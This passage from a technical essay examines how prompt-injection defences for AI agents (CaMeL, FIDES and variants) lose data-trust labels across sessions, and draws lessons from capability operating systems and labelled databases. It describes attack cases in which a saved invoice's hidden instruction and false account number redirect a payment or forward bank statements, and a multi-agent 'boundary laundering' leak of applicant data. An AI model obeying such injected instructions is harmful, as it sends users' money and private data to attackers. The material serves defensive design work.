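The labels also need to apply to individual entries. If an agent keeps its whole memory in one file, FIDES would treat the file as one variable, so adding a line from an email makes the whole file untrusted, and adding a line from a private document makes it private. A tool that searches separate entries can cause the same problem, because the formula combines the labels of everything the tool may read. FIDES avoids this if the tool returns a structured list in which each entry has its own label. *AgentKernel* (2026), a design for an agent operating system, labels each memory item separately because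 one combined label would mark the whole session as untrusted and secret and make most of the memory unusable.

*Ghost in the Agent* (2026) gives an example of saving this information, in a test built on Mem0, a memory library for agents. On the first day, an agent stores a document containing a confidential revenue forecast, and the tracking software, NeuroTaint, writes its own records to disk. Three days later, the user asks for an operations report. NeuroTaint reloads its records before the agent retrieves the document, so it can recognise the forecast in the report. *MemLineage* (2026) instead attaches the label to the memory entry itself and suggests running FIDES on top.

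### Tuesday without the labels

Suppose the developer skipped all this. On Tuesday the user asks the agent to pay the invoice. The planner starts with a clean context, and the memory contains an account number and the invoice text but no labels.

#### In CaMeL

In CaMeL, Tuesday's plan reads the saved account number and passes it to the payment tool. The interpreter must tag the number, and if no tag was stored with it, the interpreter can only apply a fixed rule to everything read from memory. The table assumes that the payment policy requires a trusted account number.

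| Rule for recalled values | Number from the emailed invoice | Number the user typed on Monday |
|---|---|---|
| Treat all memory as trusted | Pays, even if the account is the attacker's | Pays |
| Treat all memory as untrusted | Refuses | Refuses |
| Restore each entry's own tag | Refuses | Pays |

Treating all memory as untrusted is safe, but the agent then cannot use a number that the user gave it and asked it to remember. The software can distinguish that number from one that came from an untrusted source only by its stored tag.

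The hidden instruction in the invoice remains harmless in all three cases because CaMeL's planner never reads tool results, whatever their tags. A missing tag leaves the payment exposed, but it doesn't let the instruction change the plan.

#### In FIDES

FIDES is more exposed because it also uses these labels to decide what to hide from the planner. If the saved invoice comes back without a label and the software treats it as trusted and public, adding it to the context does not appear to change the context's label. FIDES therefore shows the planner the full text, including the hidden instruction. Because the context still counts as trusted, any call the planner writes after obeying the instruction also counts as trusted and passes the check on consequential calls.

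The confidentiality rule may still prevent some of the damage. If the instruction is to forward last month's bank statements, and the agent fetches them from the bank on Tuesday, they arrive with fresh labels and the software can block sending them to a stranger. The rule does not stop a payment to the attacker's account.

Microsoft warns that its released version treats a tool's output as trusted and public unless the developer labels it. A developer who adds a memory tool and forgets the label gets the failure described above. Microsoft is considering making "untrusted" the default, which would lead to the refusals in the table's second row.

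Starting a new session doesn't solve the problem either. In Microsoft's version, the context label covers what the model has read in the current run. Once an untrusted bug report enters the context, the rest of the run is untrusted unless the developer explicitly drops it. A new session clears the label, but text saved to memory returns without it. Restoring tools at the start of a session in Dongol's model has the same flaw.

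#### When memory goes into the prompt

Some agents load memory without a tool call. Das and colleagues describe agents whose software copies saved entries into the system prompt, the developer's instructions at the start of each session. FIDES labels the system prompt and the user's message trusted and public by default, although a developer can choose another label. CaMeL's planner also treats its prompt as trusted. An invoice loaded this way bypasses the protection in both systems because neither treats it as a tool result.

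This kind of failure has occurred in experiments with cooperating agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL, and asked it to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. One agent read the applicant database, where the researchers had hidden an instruction to email the data to an outside address. A coordinating agent had the data summarised and put the summary into its request to a third agent that sent messages. Neither of the first two planners saw the hidden instruction, but the third agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so its planner read the instruction and added the email to its plan. The researchers call this boundary laundering.

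They also ran AgentDojo's attacks on multi-agent versions of its tasks with five models. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL and 0.2% succeeded when each agent used CaMeL separately. Every attack in the 0.2% worked through boundary laundering. None succeeded after the researchers added two rules for communication between agents. The request that the receiving planner reads must not depend on any tool output, and other data must travel separately, as variables that keep their tags. The experiments tested only agents that call each other, but the same two rules would apply when a session leaves notes for a later one, because the boundary is similar.

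### Do newer variants track beyond one session?

CaMeLoT and SAMOS, both from 2026, extend or simplify this kind of tracking. Neither carries an individual value's label from one session to the next.

#### CaMeLoT

CaMeL checks each tool call as it happens, so an agent may do a lot of work before a policy blocks it. Nikolaou and colleagues' CaMeLoT checks the plan before anything runs. It converts the planner's program into a finite-state machine, a map of the steps the program could take, and marks each step with the tool it calls and whether the arguments are tainted. A model checker, software that explores every path through the map, then tests rules such as "a payment must not use a tainted recipient or amount." If any path breaks a rule, the planner receives a description of that path and tries to repair the plan.

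This also allows rules about a whole sequence of actions. In a simulated security office, an agent had to get approval before disconnecting a computer from the network, and had to resolve or escalate every incident ticket it opened. CaMeLoT caught all seven of the researchers' unsafe plans, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The researchers chose the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can express, so the gap was expected. On AgentDojo, CaMeLoT could fully reproduce 22 of CaMeL's 28 security policies on tool calls. The two systems agreed on whether to allow or block a plan in 59 of the 75 tasks that at least one completed or both blocked.

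The map covers a single plan from its first step to its last and records only the history of the current path. CaMeLoT rejected one plan as unsafe because it opened a ticket and left it for the day shift, which broke a rule that the plan itself must resolve or escalate the ticket. But this also means that the system cannot carry an unfinished duty into a later session.

CaMeLoT treats a value as tainted if its origin cannot be determined before the plan runs, as with a number read from a memory that mixes emailed and typed numbers. It would therefore reject Tuesday's payment even if the user had typed the account number. It would accept Monday's plan, because that plan only saves the invoice and makes no payment.

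#### SAMOS

*Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026), a master's thesis at Brown University, describes SAMOS, a system that works with the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. All tool calls pass through a gateway that enforces the rules. SAMOS labels the tools to avoid labelling every piece of data. Each tool has one label for the confidentiality of what it reads and another for what it writes to, and each label is either high or low.

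The gateway also keeps a confidentiality level for each session. The level starts at low unless the user chooses otherwise, and each tool call updates it. In the thesis's main example, an agent reads a public GitHub issue containing a hidden instruction, then tries to open a private repository. The gateway blocks the attempt because the agent has already read public content in that session.

Ntousakis's system tracks the level only within a session, and every new connection starts a new session. If an agent reads a private repository on Monday and saves a summary, Tuesday's session starts at low, with no record that the summary came from private data.

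A label on the memory tool would partly compensate, because it stays with the tool after the session ends. If the developer marks the tool as reading high-confidentiality data, recalling any memory raises the confidentiality level of Tuesday's session, whether the memory is the private summary or a note of a public holiday. If the developer marks the tool as low-confidentiality, the gateway treats the private summary as public.

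Neither setting would stop the payment to the attacker. SAMOS labels data by secrecy, not trustworthiness, so the gateway cannot mark the account number as untrusted, even on Monday.

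## How did capability operating systems keep permissions across restarts?

CaMeL and FIDES lose track of where data came from between sessions unless a developer writes code to save the labels. Some operating systems solved a similar problem for permissions decades ago. KeyKOS, which ran commercial services from 1983, and its successor EROS saved the state of the whole machine, including every running program and its permissions, every few minutes. After a power failure, the programs resumed with the same permissions.

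These systems use capabilities in the older sense, as rights that a program holds. Tymshare, a company that sold computer time to customers who did not always trust each other, began developing KeyKOS in 1975. EROS, a research system led by Jonathan Shapiro, adopted KeyKOS's published design in 1991. CapROS continued EROS's development under Charles Landau, one of KeyKOS's designers. Coyotos, which also grew out of EROS, was Shapiro's attempt to build a new kernel simple enough to prove correct. A kernel is the core of an operating system and has full control of the hardware.

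### The confused deputy

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes the incident that convinced Hardy, then an engineer at Tymshare, that capabilities were necessary. Tymshare's customers shared a compiler and could give it the name of a file for debugging output. The compiler also recorded usage statistics in a system directory, so Tymshare had given it permission to write to any file there, including the billing records. One customer named the billing file as the place for debugging output, and the compiler overwrote it.

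The compiler had authority from two sources, Tymshare and the customer, but could not specify which it was using to open a file. Hardy considered having it check file names, but a list of forbidden names would need updating whenever someone added a sensitive file, and some customers had a right to write in the system directory. Tymshare then added a command that let a program choose between its two authorities, but some programs soon needed more than two.

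In a capability system, the compiler would hold one capability for the statistics file, and the customer would pass it another for the debugging output. A customer who had no right to change the billing file would have no capability for that file, and so could not pass one to the compiler. Because a capability both identifies a file and grants the right to use it, the compiler could not use Tymshare's permission to write to a file the customer chose.

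Rajani, Garg and Rezk (2016), in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, later proved that capabilities differ fundamentally from ordinary access control. They also gave the first formal definition of what it means for a program to be free from confused deputy attacks.

### One store for memory and disk

On a conventional computer, a program's memory disappears when the machine shuts down. To keep data, the program must write it to a file, and after a restart it must open that file again by name. The operating system allows or refuses the request to open it, usually based on which user is running the program.

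KeyKOS and EROS have a single-level store, in which programs treat everything as memory and the kernel moves data to and from disk. Shapiro and Adams (2002), in *Design Evolution of the EROS Single-Level Store*, argue that a machine that never crashed would need no file system, because it could use the whole disk as an extension of memory. Real machines crash, so the kernel regularly saves a consistent copy of everything, called a checkpoint.

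The store contains two kinds of object, pages that hold data and nodes that hold capabilities. In KeyKOS, a page has 4,096 bytes and a node has 16 slots, each for one capability. A program can write any data to its pages but cannot write the bits of a capability. To use a capability, it gives the kernel a slot number. In *Security in KeyKOS*, Rajunas, Hardy and colleagues explain that this separation prevents programs from forging capabilities.

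Nodes also record the state of each running program, including the instruction it has reached and the capabilities it holds. The kernel keeps other tables for speed, but it can rebuild them all from pages and nodes.

### How a checkpoint works

CapROS's *The Checkpoint Mechanism* describes a procedure derived from EROS, which in turn adapted it from KeyKOS:

1. Before a program changes a page or node, the kernel reserves room for the new version in a log, a separate area of the disk.
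2. Typically every five minutes, the kernel briefly stops all programs. It marks every changed object "copy on write" and notes which programs are running. If a program later changes a marked object, it changes a copy, and the version from the moment of the snapshot stays intact.
3. The programs resume while the kernel writes the snapshot to the log, along with a directory of where each object is.
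4. The kernel writes a short header that identifies the checkpoint as complete. If the machine crashes before this step finishes, it restarts from the previous checkpoint.
5. In the background, the system copies objects from the log to their permanent places on disk, and can then reuse the log space.

CapROS keeps the two most recent headers, so if a write fails, one valid header remains. On restart, the kernel reads both, picks the newer valid one, and reloads the directory and the list of running programs. Each program continues from where it was at the snapshot.

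Bomberger, Frantz and colleagues report in *The KeyKOS Nanokernel Architecture* that a program can detect a restart only as an unexplained jump in the clock, if at all. At the UNIFORUM conference in 1990, the company that then owned KeyKOS invited visitors to have a running machine unplugged. Within 30 seconds of power returning, the machine was working again with the same windows on the screen.

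### Why no one has to grant the rights again

A program's capabilities survive a restart because they are stored in nodes, which each checkpoint saves together with pages. For example, a backup program that holds a read-only capability for one folder will hold exactly that capability after a restart, and no start-up script has to grant it. The checkpoint also records rights and data at the same instant, so a crash cannot leave a new document with the permissions of an old one.

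The kernel must also handle capabilities for things that no longer exist. If a program deletes a page and the system reuses the space, an old capability should not give access to the new contents. In the first two EROS designs that Shapiro and Adams describe, each capability stores the number of times the system had allocated that space when it issued the capability. The disk holds the current count, and the capability works only if the two match.

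Connections to anything outside the checkpoint need special treatment. For example, CapROS does not save the time when a sleeping program should wake, so on restart it wakes the program with a code indicating that the system restarted. The program must then work out whether it still needs to wait.

### Confinement

Confinement means running a program on private data while ensuring that it cannot pass the data to anyone without permission. In EROS, a trusted component called a constructor creates new copies of a program (Shapiro, 2005, *The EROS Constructor*). The constructor checks the capabilities the developer built into the program. If none of them can carry information out, a new copy can communicate only through channels the user gives it. KeyKOS has a similar component called a factory.

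In KeyKOS, a program with ordinary read-only access to a node could still take out a stronger capability stored there and use it to change other objects. The designers therefore added the sense key, which weakens every capability that a program obtains through it, however many nodes the program passes through. EROS has an equivalent. In a 2005 mailing-list reply on confinement, Shapiro explains that these capabilities can refer only to objects that the kernel implements, which excludes capabilities for sending messages to another program.

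Shapiro and Samuel Weber published a proof of the EROS confinement mechanism in 2000. They modelled what programs can do with capabilities and proved that a few checks before a program starts are enough to confine it, whatever its code does afterwards. The proof covers a model of the system, and Shapiro acknowledges in *Thinking About Capabilities* (2004) that no one had verified the implementation.

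A restart does not weaken confinement as long as the checkpoint is accurate. The program returns with the same capabilities, so the user does not need to repeat the checks.

### What checkpoints cost

In *EROS checkpointing and memory management* (1999), Shapiro reports that taking the snapshot stopped the machine for about 50 milliseconds every five minutes, or about 0.017% of the time. The kernel then has to write the changed data to disk, but it can do so in large sequential writes, which suit a spinning disk. He puts EROS's sustained writing speed at 2.5 to 3 times that of the best Unix systems.

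Shapiro and Adams calculated that saving 400 kilobytes of file data on a particular disk would take a conventional system 231 milliseconds and EROS 138, including the time EROS later spent copying the data to its permanent locations. They based this partly on measurements from KeyKOS, where more than half of changed objects were deleted or changed again before the system had to copy them. They had not yet measured complete applications on EROS.

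Checkpoints slow programs more when they constantly rewrite most of the machine's memory. Iain McClatchie, a chip designer, described a program that overwrote 100 megabytes almost 1,000 times in ten minutes. He estimated that checkpoints could stop it for 10 to 15 seconds every five minutes, a slowdown of about 5%. In his reply, *Re: Questions about EROS* (1999), Shapiro agreed that this was a serious problem for such programs and suggested checkpointing less often or buying more memory.

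Shapiro, Smith and Farber (1999) found in *EROS* that the system's basic operations were about as fast as similar ones in Linux, so capabilities did not make the rest of EROS slow. According to their conference slides, creating a process took 0.66 milliseconds in EROS and 1.92 in Linux, although the simplest request to the kernel took 1.6 microseconds in EROS and 0.7 in Linux.

### Revoking a stored right

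Programs in KeyKOS can copy their capabilities and pass them on, so the owner of an object may not know who has access to it. Deleting the object stops every copy from working, but the owner loses the object too. To be able to revoke access to a calendar without deleting it, the owner can give out a capability for a forwarding object that relays requests to the calendar. Destroying the forwarding object cuts off everyone who used it and leaves the owner's own access intact. Lecture notes from the University of New South Wales (2002) describe how a trusted EROS component inserts these objects when programs exchange capabilities.

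Persistence makes this planning more important. On a conventional system, a program must open its files again after a restart, and the system may refuse. Several KeyKOS machines ran for more than three years, through power failures, without losing their running programs, so a forgotten capability could stay valid for just as long.

A crash can also undo a revocation. If the owner destroys a forwarding object after the last checkpoint and the machine then fails, the machine restarts with the object still in place. KeyKOS lets databases save individual pages immediately so that they do not lose recent transactions, but this does not protect revocations because pages cannot hold capabilities. A revocation is sure to survive a crash only once the next checkpoint is complete.

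### Saving a faulty state

A checkpoint preserves errors along with everything else. A participant in a 1999 Linux mailing-list thread, *Some very thought-provoking ideas about OS architecture*, described a possible failure in which a bug corrupts memory, EROS saves the corrupted memory to disk, and the system crashes a few minutes later. After restarting, the system loads the same corrupted memory and crashes again. In the same thread, the Linux developer Alan Cox (1999) argued that no one had found a good way to repair this kind of store after losing part of it.

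EROS checks that the system's state is consistent before saving it, which reduces the danger of making errors permanent. Shapiro and Adams warn that L3 and Fluke, two other systems with checkpoints, had no such check and so ran this risk. KeyKOS also keeps at least two copies of every node on disk, because losing capabilities would be especially damaging.

These measures do not detect a program's own mistakes. A page can contain a wrong account number and still be consistent by the kernel's standards. McClatchie pointed out that his chip-design software crashed every month or two without harming his work, because it saved designs to disk in a simple format separate from its complicated working memory. Shapiro replied that this safety came from the simple format and the boundary around it, and that a persistent system could offer both by having a small, carefully written program store documents.

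### Why seL4 leaves persistence out

seL4, a capability-based kernel whose developers proved its code correct in 2009, does not save capabilities across restarts. When the machine starts, seL4 gives one initial program control of the free memory. That program creates the others and hands out their rights, for example from a description that a developer has written.

seL4's design follows a rule from Jochen Liedtke, who created the L4 family of kernels to which it belongs, that a kernel should contain only what cannot work outside it. Checkpointing can work outside the kernel, and Liedtke's earlier L3 system ran it in an ordinary program. Shapiro and Adams were also moving most of it out of the kernel in their version of EROS for embedded devices, because they had decided to remove the disk drivers from the kernel and a separate program now had to write the checkpoints. Leaving a feature out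 of a kernel also makes the kernel easier to prove correct.

seL4 relies on the initial program and its description to grant the correct rights at every start, but a restart clears any corrupted state that has not been written to disk.

### What carries over to agent memory

The most useful lesson for an agent is to store authority separately from data and never infer it from the data's content. Writing "this program may change the billing file" in a KeyKOS page would not give the program that permission. Similarly, a saved note that reads "the user has approved payments to this account" should not change what the payment tool allows. The approval should be in a separate record that only the software around the models can write. That would also prevent the drift from preference to permission that Ding and colleagues describe.

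The software should also save a value and its label in one step. If it saves the account number first and crashes before saving the "untrusted" label, Tuesday's session loads a number with no label. A checkpoint prevents this by saving the whole machine at once, but an agent can get the same protection from a database that completes either both writes or neither.

Capabilities could even stop Tuesday's payment from going to the attacker. If the user had set up Acme as a payee earlier, the bank could have issued a capability that allowed payments only to Acme's account. The agent would store that capability and use it on Tuesday, taking only the amount from the invoice. The false account number would then have no effect, just as the customer's file name would have had none if the compiler had needed a capability for the billing file. This protection depends on setting up the payee with the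 right account. If the user took the account number from the false invoice, every payment made with the capability would go to the attacker.

Capability systems offer much less protection against text that persuades its reader. They control which objects a program may use. Reading an ordinary document does not normally change what a conventional program tries to do, but it can change what a language model tries to do. Suppose a planner may read the mailbox and send messages, and a saved invoice tells it to forward bank statements. If the planner complies, the kernel allows it because the planner is using valid capabilities.

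Confinement suits the quarantined model better. A model that starts with no tools and no outside connections still has none after a restart, so an instruction in a saved invoice cannot make it send anything, though its summaries are still as untrusted as the invoice.

A capability also does not record who wrote the data in a page, such as a saved account number. To track that, a system has to label the data itself, as the research operating system HiStar does.

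## How do information-flow databases keep labels on stored data?

Several older systems label stored data and enforce the labels whenever a program reads the data again, even years later. *IFDB* (Schultz and Liskov, 2013) does this for every row in a database, and HiStar does it for everything on a machine's disk. Both had to deal with programs that read a lot of stored data and picked up so many restrictions that they could no longer do their jobs, which is also a problem for agents.

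### Denning's lattice and Biba's rules

The theory behind these systems comes from the 1970s. Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, assigns each piece of data a security class and specifies which classes information may flow between. The classes form a lattice, which means that any two of them have a single least restrictive class that is at least as strict as both. If a program computes $c$ from $a$ and $b$, software needs only one check,

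$$\underline{a} \oplus \underline{b} \to \underline{c},$$

where $\underline{a}$ is the class of $a$, $\oplus$ combines two classes and $\to$ means "may flow to".

The maximum-and-minimum rule in FIDES uses a simple lattice whose levels form a line. In other lattices, some classes cannot be ranked against each other. If a clinic labels Ann's records {Ann} and Bob's records {Bob}, neither label is stricter than the other, and a report that uses both gets {Ann, Bob}. With $n$ patients, there are $2^n$ possible labels.

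A label can also be a logical formula. In *disjunction-category labels*, which *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions* (2012) uses, a label has a secrecy formula $S$ and an integrity formula $I$, and two labels combine as

$$\langle S_1, I_1 \rangle \sqcup \langle S_2, I_2 \rangle = \langle S_1 \wedge S_2,\ I_1 \vee I_2 \rangle.$$

A report on Ann and Bob has the secrecy formula "Ann and Bob", so both must agree before anyone releases it. A payment order that combines the user's reference with Acme's account number has the integrity formula "user or Acme", because either could have influenced it. Policies can use this formula to make finer distinctions than the label "untrusted" would allow.

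Early military rules for confidentiality forbade a program to read data above its level or write data below it. Kenneth Biba turned these rules around to protect integrity in MITRE's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977). He proposed three policies, which correspond closely to the ways an agent can handle an untrusted email:

- **Strict integrity.** A program may not read data less trusted than itself or write data more trusted than itself. The planner in the dual-LLM pattern works this way, since it never reads the email.
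- **Ring.** A program may read anything and keeps its level, but still cannot write to a higher one. An ordinary agent resembles this, because it reads the email and can still make payments.
- **Low-water mark.** A program may read anything, but its level falls to that of the least trusted data it has read. The context label in FIDES works this way.

The textbook *Invitation to Cybersecurity* explains that the low-water mark exists because low-level information may be misleading or incomplete, and so "pollutes" whoever reads it.

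Integrity labels do not protect against a program's own mistakes. Lecture slides from Purdue University's *Access Control* course point out that a program cannot leak a secret it has never read, but it can introduce bad data without having read any. For example, a planner might invent an account number when nothing in its context is untrusted. The number would still get a trusted label, because no outsider influenced it.

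### How IFDB works

Schultz and Liskov built IFDB by modifying PostgreSQL, a widely used database. They wanted to protect each person's records from the other people whose data is in the same database. Normally the application does this. It has access to everyone's data, so one forgotten check in its code can expose all of it.

In IFDB, a secrecy label is a set of tags, such as `alice_medical`. Every row has a label, and so does every process (a running program that connects to the database). A process can add a tag to its label to read more, but it can remove a tag, which is called declassifying, only if it has authority for that tag. A process can send data to the outside world only when its label is empty, so a process that has read Alice's medical records and has no authority over them cannot send anything out.

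#### Query by Label

IFDB's main idea is a rule called Query by Label. A process with label $L_P$ gets the same result as if the database contained only the rows whose labels $L_t$ satisfy

$$L_t \subseteq L_P.$$

Suppose a table has one row each for Alice, Bob and Cat, and each row carries that patient's tag. If a process whose label contains the tags for Alice and Bob queries the whole table, it gets only their two rows, and a count of the patients returns two. The database omits Cat's row without raising an error, because an error would reveal that the row exists. It also doesn't add Cat's tag to the process's label.

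Under IFDB's Query by Label, the programmer chooses a process's label before running a query, and the query can return only rows that the label covers. This matters most for large tables. If IFDB instead raised the label to cover every row that a query examined, searching a table of 10,000 patients would leave the process with 10,000 tags.

New rows get the same label as the process that writes them, and a process can change or delete only rows with its own label. Buiras, Levy and colleagues (2013) explain in *Decentralized Information Flow Control with the LIO library* why writing needs this stricter condition. When an editor saves a file, information flows into the file but also back to the editor, for example in the message that reports whether the save worked. The two labels must therefore allow information to flow in both directions, which is possible only if they are equal.

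IFDB also has integrity labels. Query by Label lets an application limit both the confidentiality and the integrity of the data it receives (Schultz, 2012, *Decentralized information flow control for databases*). An agent's payment program could use it to request only rows that no outsider has influenced.

#### Declassifying views

A database view is a stored query that programs can read like a table. In IFDB a view can have authority attached, so that it removes certain tags from the rows it returns. Conference-reviewing software, for example, might keep everyone's contact details secret but publish the names of the committee. In simplified form:

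```
CREATE VIEW CommitteeNames AS
  SELECT name FROM Contacts WHERE on_committee
  WITH DECLASSIFYING (all_contacts);
```

Any program can read the names through this view without adding the `all_contacts` tag to its label. The programmer who creates the view must have authority for that tag. Reviewers then need to check one short query instead of every page that displays a committee member's name.

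*Secure Serverless Computing Using Dynamic Information Flow Control* (2018) describes a similar tool for small cloud programs. For example, a credit agency may want to publish how many people fall into each score band. The count uses every customer's history, so it initially carries all their labels. The agency can define a declassifier with an upper label $h$, a lower label $l$ and a function $D$ that does the counting. If the calling program's label is between $l$ and $h$, inclusive, the declassifier runs with label $l$. Otherwise it runs with the caller's label.

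The upper label prevents misuse. If a program has also read medical records, its label is outside the range, so calling the credit declassifier removes nothing. Any declassifier still breaks non-interference by design, since non-interference means that secrets have no effect on public results. The paper's proofs cover only the system without declassifiers.

#### Committing a transaction

A transaction is a group of database operations that all take effect or all fail. This all-or-nothing behaviour can leak a secret:

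1. A process with an empty label starts a transaction and inserts a public row stating that Alice is ill.
2. It adds `alice_medical` to its label and reads her record.
3. If she is ill, it commits the transaction. If not, it cancels, and the public row disappears.

Each step obeys the rules for reading and writing, but anyone who can see the public table now knows whether Alice is ill.

IFDB prevents this by checking the label at the moment of commit, $L_C$. The transaction can commit only if

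$$L_C \subseteq L_t \quad \text{for every row } t \text{ it wrote}.$$

In the example, $L_C$ contains `alice_medical` and the public row's label is empty, so the database refuses the commit and the public row never appears, whatever Alice's record contains. A programmer with a legitimate reason to combine the two steps can declassify before committing, or read the medical record in a separate transaction.

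An agent that saves its notes in a batch needs the same rule for integrity. If it drafts a trusted note and then reads a stranger's email before saving, the software should give the batch the session's label at the time of saving, not at the time of drafting.

#### What labels cost

With a real web application, IFDB handled as many requests per second as unmodified PostgreSQL, though individual requests took about 24% longer. In a test based on TPC-C, a standard benchmark that simulates order processing, its throughput was about 1% lower. Schultz and Liskov also extended PHP and Python so that labels followed data out of the database and into the program. Moving two existing web applications to this platform exposed several security bugs and prevented information leaks.

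IFDB labels whole rows, not individual fields, so an agent would need separate rows for a payee name that the user typed and an account number from an email. IFDB has no formal proof that its rules prevent every leak.

### Two values for one key

In an ordinary database, every row of a table has a unique key, such as a flight number, and the database rejects a second row with the same key. This rule can reveal hidden rows to users who aren't allowed to see them. A report on military databases by the US National Computer Security Center uses a table of flights and their cargo. Suppose flight 73 has a secret row that lists missiles as its cargo. A clerk without clearance cannot see this row and tries to add a flight 73 carrying food. If the database rejects the new row as a duplicate, the clerk learns that a secret flight 73 exists.

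Multilevel databases, which store data at several levels of secrecy, can avoid this by accepting both rows. This is called polyinstantiation:

| Flight | Cargo | Level | Who sees the row |
|---|---|---|---|
| 73 | Food | Unclassified | Everyone |
| 73 | Missiles | Secret | Cleared users |

IFDB does the same when a new row's key clashes with that of a row the process cannot see.

The conflict can also start at the secret level. Slides from the University of Tennessee at Chattanooga's *Multilevel Security (MLS)* (2021) course give the example of a cleared user who adds a secret salary for an employee who already has an unclassified one. If the database refused the new value, the cleared user could not record it. If it overwrote the old value, uncleared users would see the change and know that something had happened. If it kept both, the unclassified value could serve as a cover story, which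 is false information that hides the existence of the real value.

The drawback is that a cleared user who looks up flight 73 finds two answers. The labels show who may see each row but not which row is true. Jajodia and Sandhu observed in *Toward a Multilevel Secure Relational Data Model* (1991) that there was still no agreement on how such a database should behave. Some later designs create a second version only when a user explicitly asks for one.

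An agent's memory has the same conflict over integrity. Suppose the user typed Acme's account number in March, and an email in June gives a different one. If the agent overwrites the old number, a forged email could redirect payments. If it discards the new one, it will miss a genuine change of bank. Keeping both, each with its own label, lets the payment tool use the number from March while the agent tells the user that an email gave a different one.

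### Labels on everything: HiStar and Asbestos

Zeldovich, Boyd-Wickizer and colleagues, in *Making Information Flow Explicit in HiStar* (2006), extended labels from a single database to a whole operating system. HiStar has no all-powerful administrator account, and its kernel is the only fully trusted code. jad-reads (2009), a blog of notes on systems papers, summarises the rules. The thread (a running strand of a program) that creates an object must give it a label, which never changes. A thread's own label can rise to let it read restricted objects, but only up to a limit called its clearance.

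For example, a virus scanner has to read all of a user's private files, so its label rises to cover them. From then on it cannot write to the network, because the network's label is lower. Even if an attacker takes over the scanner, it cannot send the files over the network.

HiStar keeps all its objects on disk in a single-level store like the one in EROS, so it restores the labels along with the data after a restart. Programs don't have to save the labels themselves, a step that a developer of a CaMeL or FIDES agent can forget.

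HiStar's labels descend from those of Asbestos, an operating system that Efstathopoulos, Krohn and colleagues presented in 2005 in *Labels and Event Processes in the Asbestos Operating System*. Asbestos labels float, meaning that when a process receives a message from a tainted process, the kernel automatically adds the taint to the receiver. According to notes on Asbestos by developers of the GNU Hurd, another operating system, the taint on data passes to any information derived from it, and only the data's original owner, whether a person or a program, can authorise removing the taint.

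Floating labels are convenient because programs need no changes to work with them, but a change in a label can itself leak information. For example, a tainted process can leak a secret bit by sending a message to a clean helper if the bit is 1 and doing nothing if it is 0. The message taints the helper, which can then no longer use the network. An observer who expects to hear from the helper every minute learns the bit from whether its next message arrives. HiStar closes this channel by requiring a thread to request a higher label before it can read restricted data. The kernel never raises a thread's label because of another thread's actions.

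Floating labels also cause trouble for a server with many users. After a web server handles Ann's data and then Bob's, it has both taints and can't reply to either of them. Efstathopoulos and colleagues solved this with event processes, lightweight contexts that isolate each user's data within one server process. An agent could similarly handle each supplier's messages in a separate context, so that one supplier's email doesn't taint its work for another.

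### LOMAC and the loss of rights

LOMAC, a module for Linux that Timothy Fraser presented in 2000, applies Biba's low-water mark policy to ordinary computers. It gives each file a high or low integrity level and treats anything from the network as low. When a high-level process reads low-level data, LOMAC demotes the process, which can then no longer change high-level files. If a user opens a downloaded file that contains a virus, the virus cannot alter the operating system.

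A process can receive low-level data without opening a file, through a pipe that passes another program's output directly to it. Fraser explains in *LWM*, a message to a FreeBSD mailing list, that LOMAC also demotes a process that reads low-level data from a pipe. Linux users connect programs this way so often that exempting pipes would have made the protection much weaker.

The longer a process runs, the more likely it is to read something that demotes it. The loss often shows up later, in an unrelated operation. For example, a program might start at the high level, open a system log, read a downloaded file an hour later, and then fail when it next writes to the log. Researchers at Stony Brook University call this self-revocation because the process caused its own loss of privileges. Most programs have no code to handle this because their programmers assumed that a permission would last.

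The Stony Brook group proposed a variant called Self-Revocation Free Downgrading, which lets a process fall to a lower level only if it keeps every privilege it is already using. Otherwise the read fails. An agent with a low-water-mark policy could do the same by checking, before it loads an untrusted memory, whether loading it would block a tool that the user's request needs. If so, the agent could leave the memory hidden or ask the user before it is partway through the task.

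### Label creep

Label creep is the tendency of labels to become more restrictive as data from many sources is mixed. Each new input can add restrictions but never remove them. The credit agency's count, for example, starts with the restrictions of every customer in the file.

An agent with persistent memory is especially exposed, because it mixes old data into every new task. Suppose that a share $u$ of its memories is untrusted and that the software loads $k$ of them at random into the planner's context. The chance that none is untrusted is

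$$(1-u)^k.$$

If 20% of memories are untrusted and the software loads ten, the chance that all ten are trusted is $0.8^{10} \approx 0.107$, or about 11%. In the other 89% of sessions, the planner's context is untrusted from the start, and a FIDES-style policy would block every payment the planner tried to make.

| Untrusted share of memory | 5 memories loaded | 10 loaded | 20 loaded |
|---|---|---|---|
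| 1% | 95% | 90% | 82% |
| 5% | 77% | 60% | 36% |
| 20% | 33% | 11% | 1% |

*Chance that no loaded memory is untrusted.*

An agent that retrieves ten memories would need to keep the untrusted share below about 6.7% to have an even chance of a clean context. The chance falls if it searches its memory several times in one task. If 20% of memories are untrusted, five searches of ten memories each leave a clean context in about one task in 70,000.

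Real retrieval software picks the memories that best match the request, not a random sample, so the odds of retrieving untrusted text depend on the request. A question about the user's favourite airline will mostly match things the user said. A request to pay Acme will mostly match Acme's emails, so the context is most likely to be untrusted when the user wants a consequential action.

Label creep also compounds, because each new note takes the label of the context in which the planner decided to save it. If 20% of memories are untrusted and ten are loaded at random each time, 89% of new notes would be untrusted even if the agent never read another email. As those notes accumulate, the untrusted share rises and the chance of a clean session falls. FIDES would avoid this by hiding the untrusted memories behind variable names, but the planner would then be unable to read them.

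### Lessons for agent memory

#### Filter by label before ranking

A memory search usually scores each entry by how well it matches the request and returns the top ten. If software removes untrusted entries only after this search, an attacker can crowd out the trusted ones. For example, fifty emails about Acme's bank account could lead to fifty closely matching notes, which take all ten places. The filter then removes all ten, and the planner receives nothing, even though the account number the user typed in March is still in the store.

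Query by Label suggests the opposite order, in which the software first selects the entries that the planner may read and then ranks only those. This way, the fifty notes have no effect on the result, provided that the scores also ignore hidden entries. Some search methods give rare words more weight. If they measure rarity across the whole store, an attacker can still change the ranking of trusted entries by changing how rare a word is.

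For Tuesday's payment, filtering first gives the planner the number the user typed, if the user typed one. If the only Acme number came from the invoice, the search returns nothing, and the agent can ask the user for the number at the start.

#### Keep trusted and untrusted versions apart

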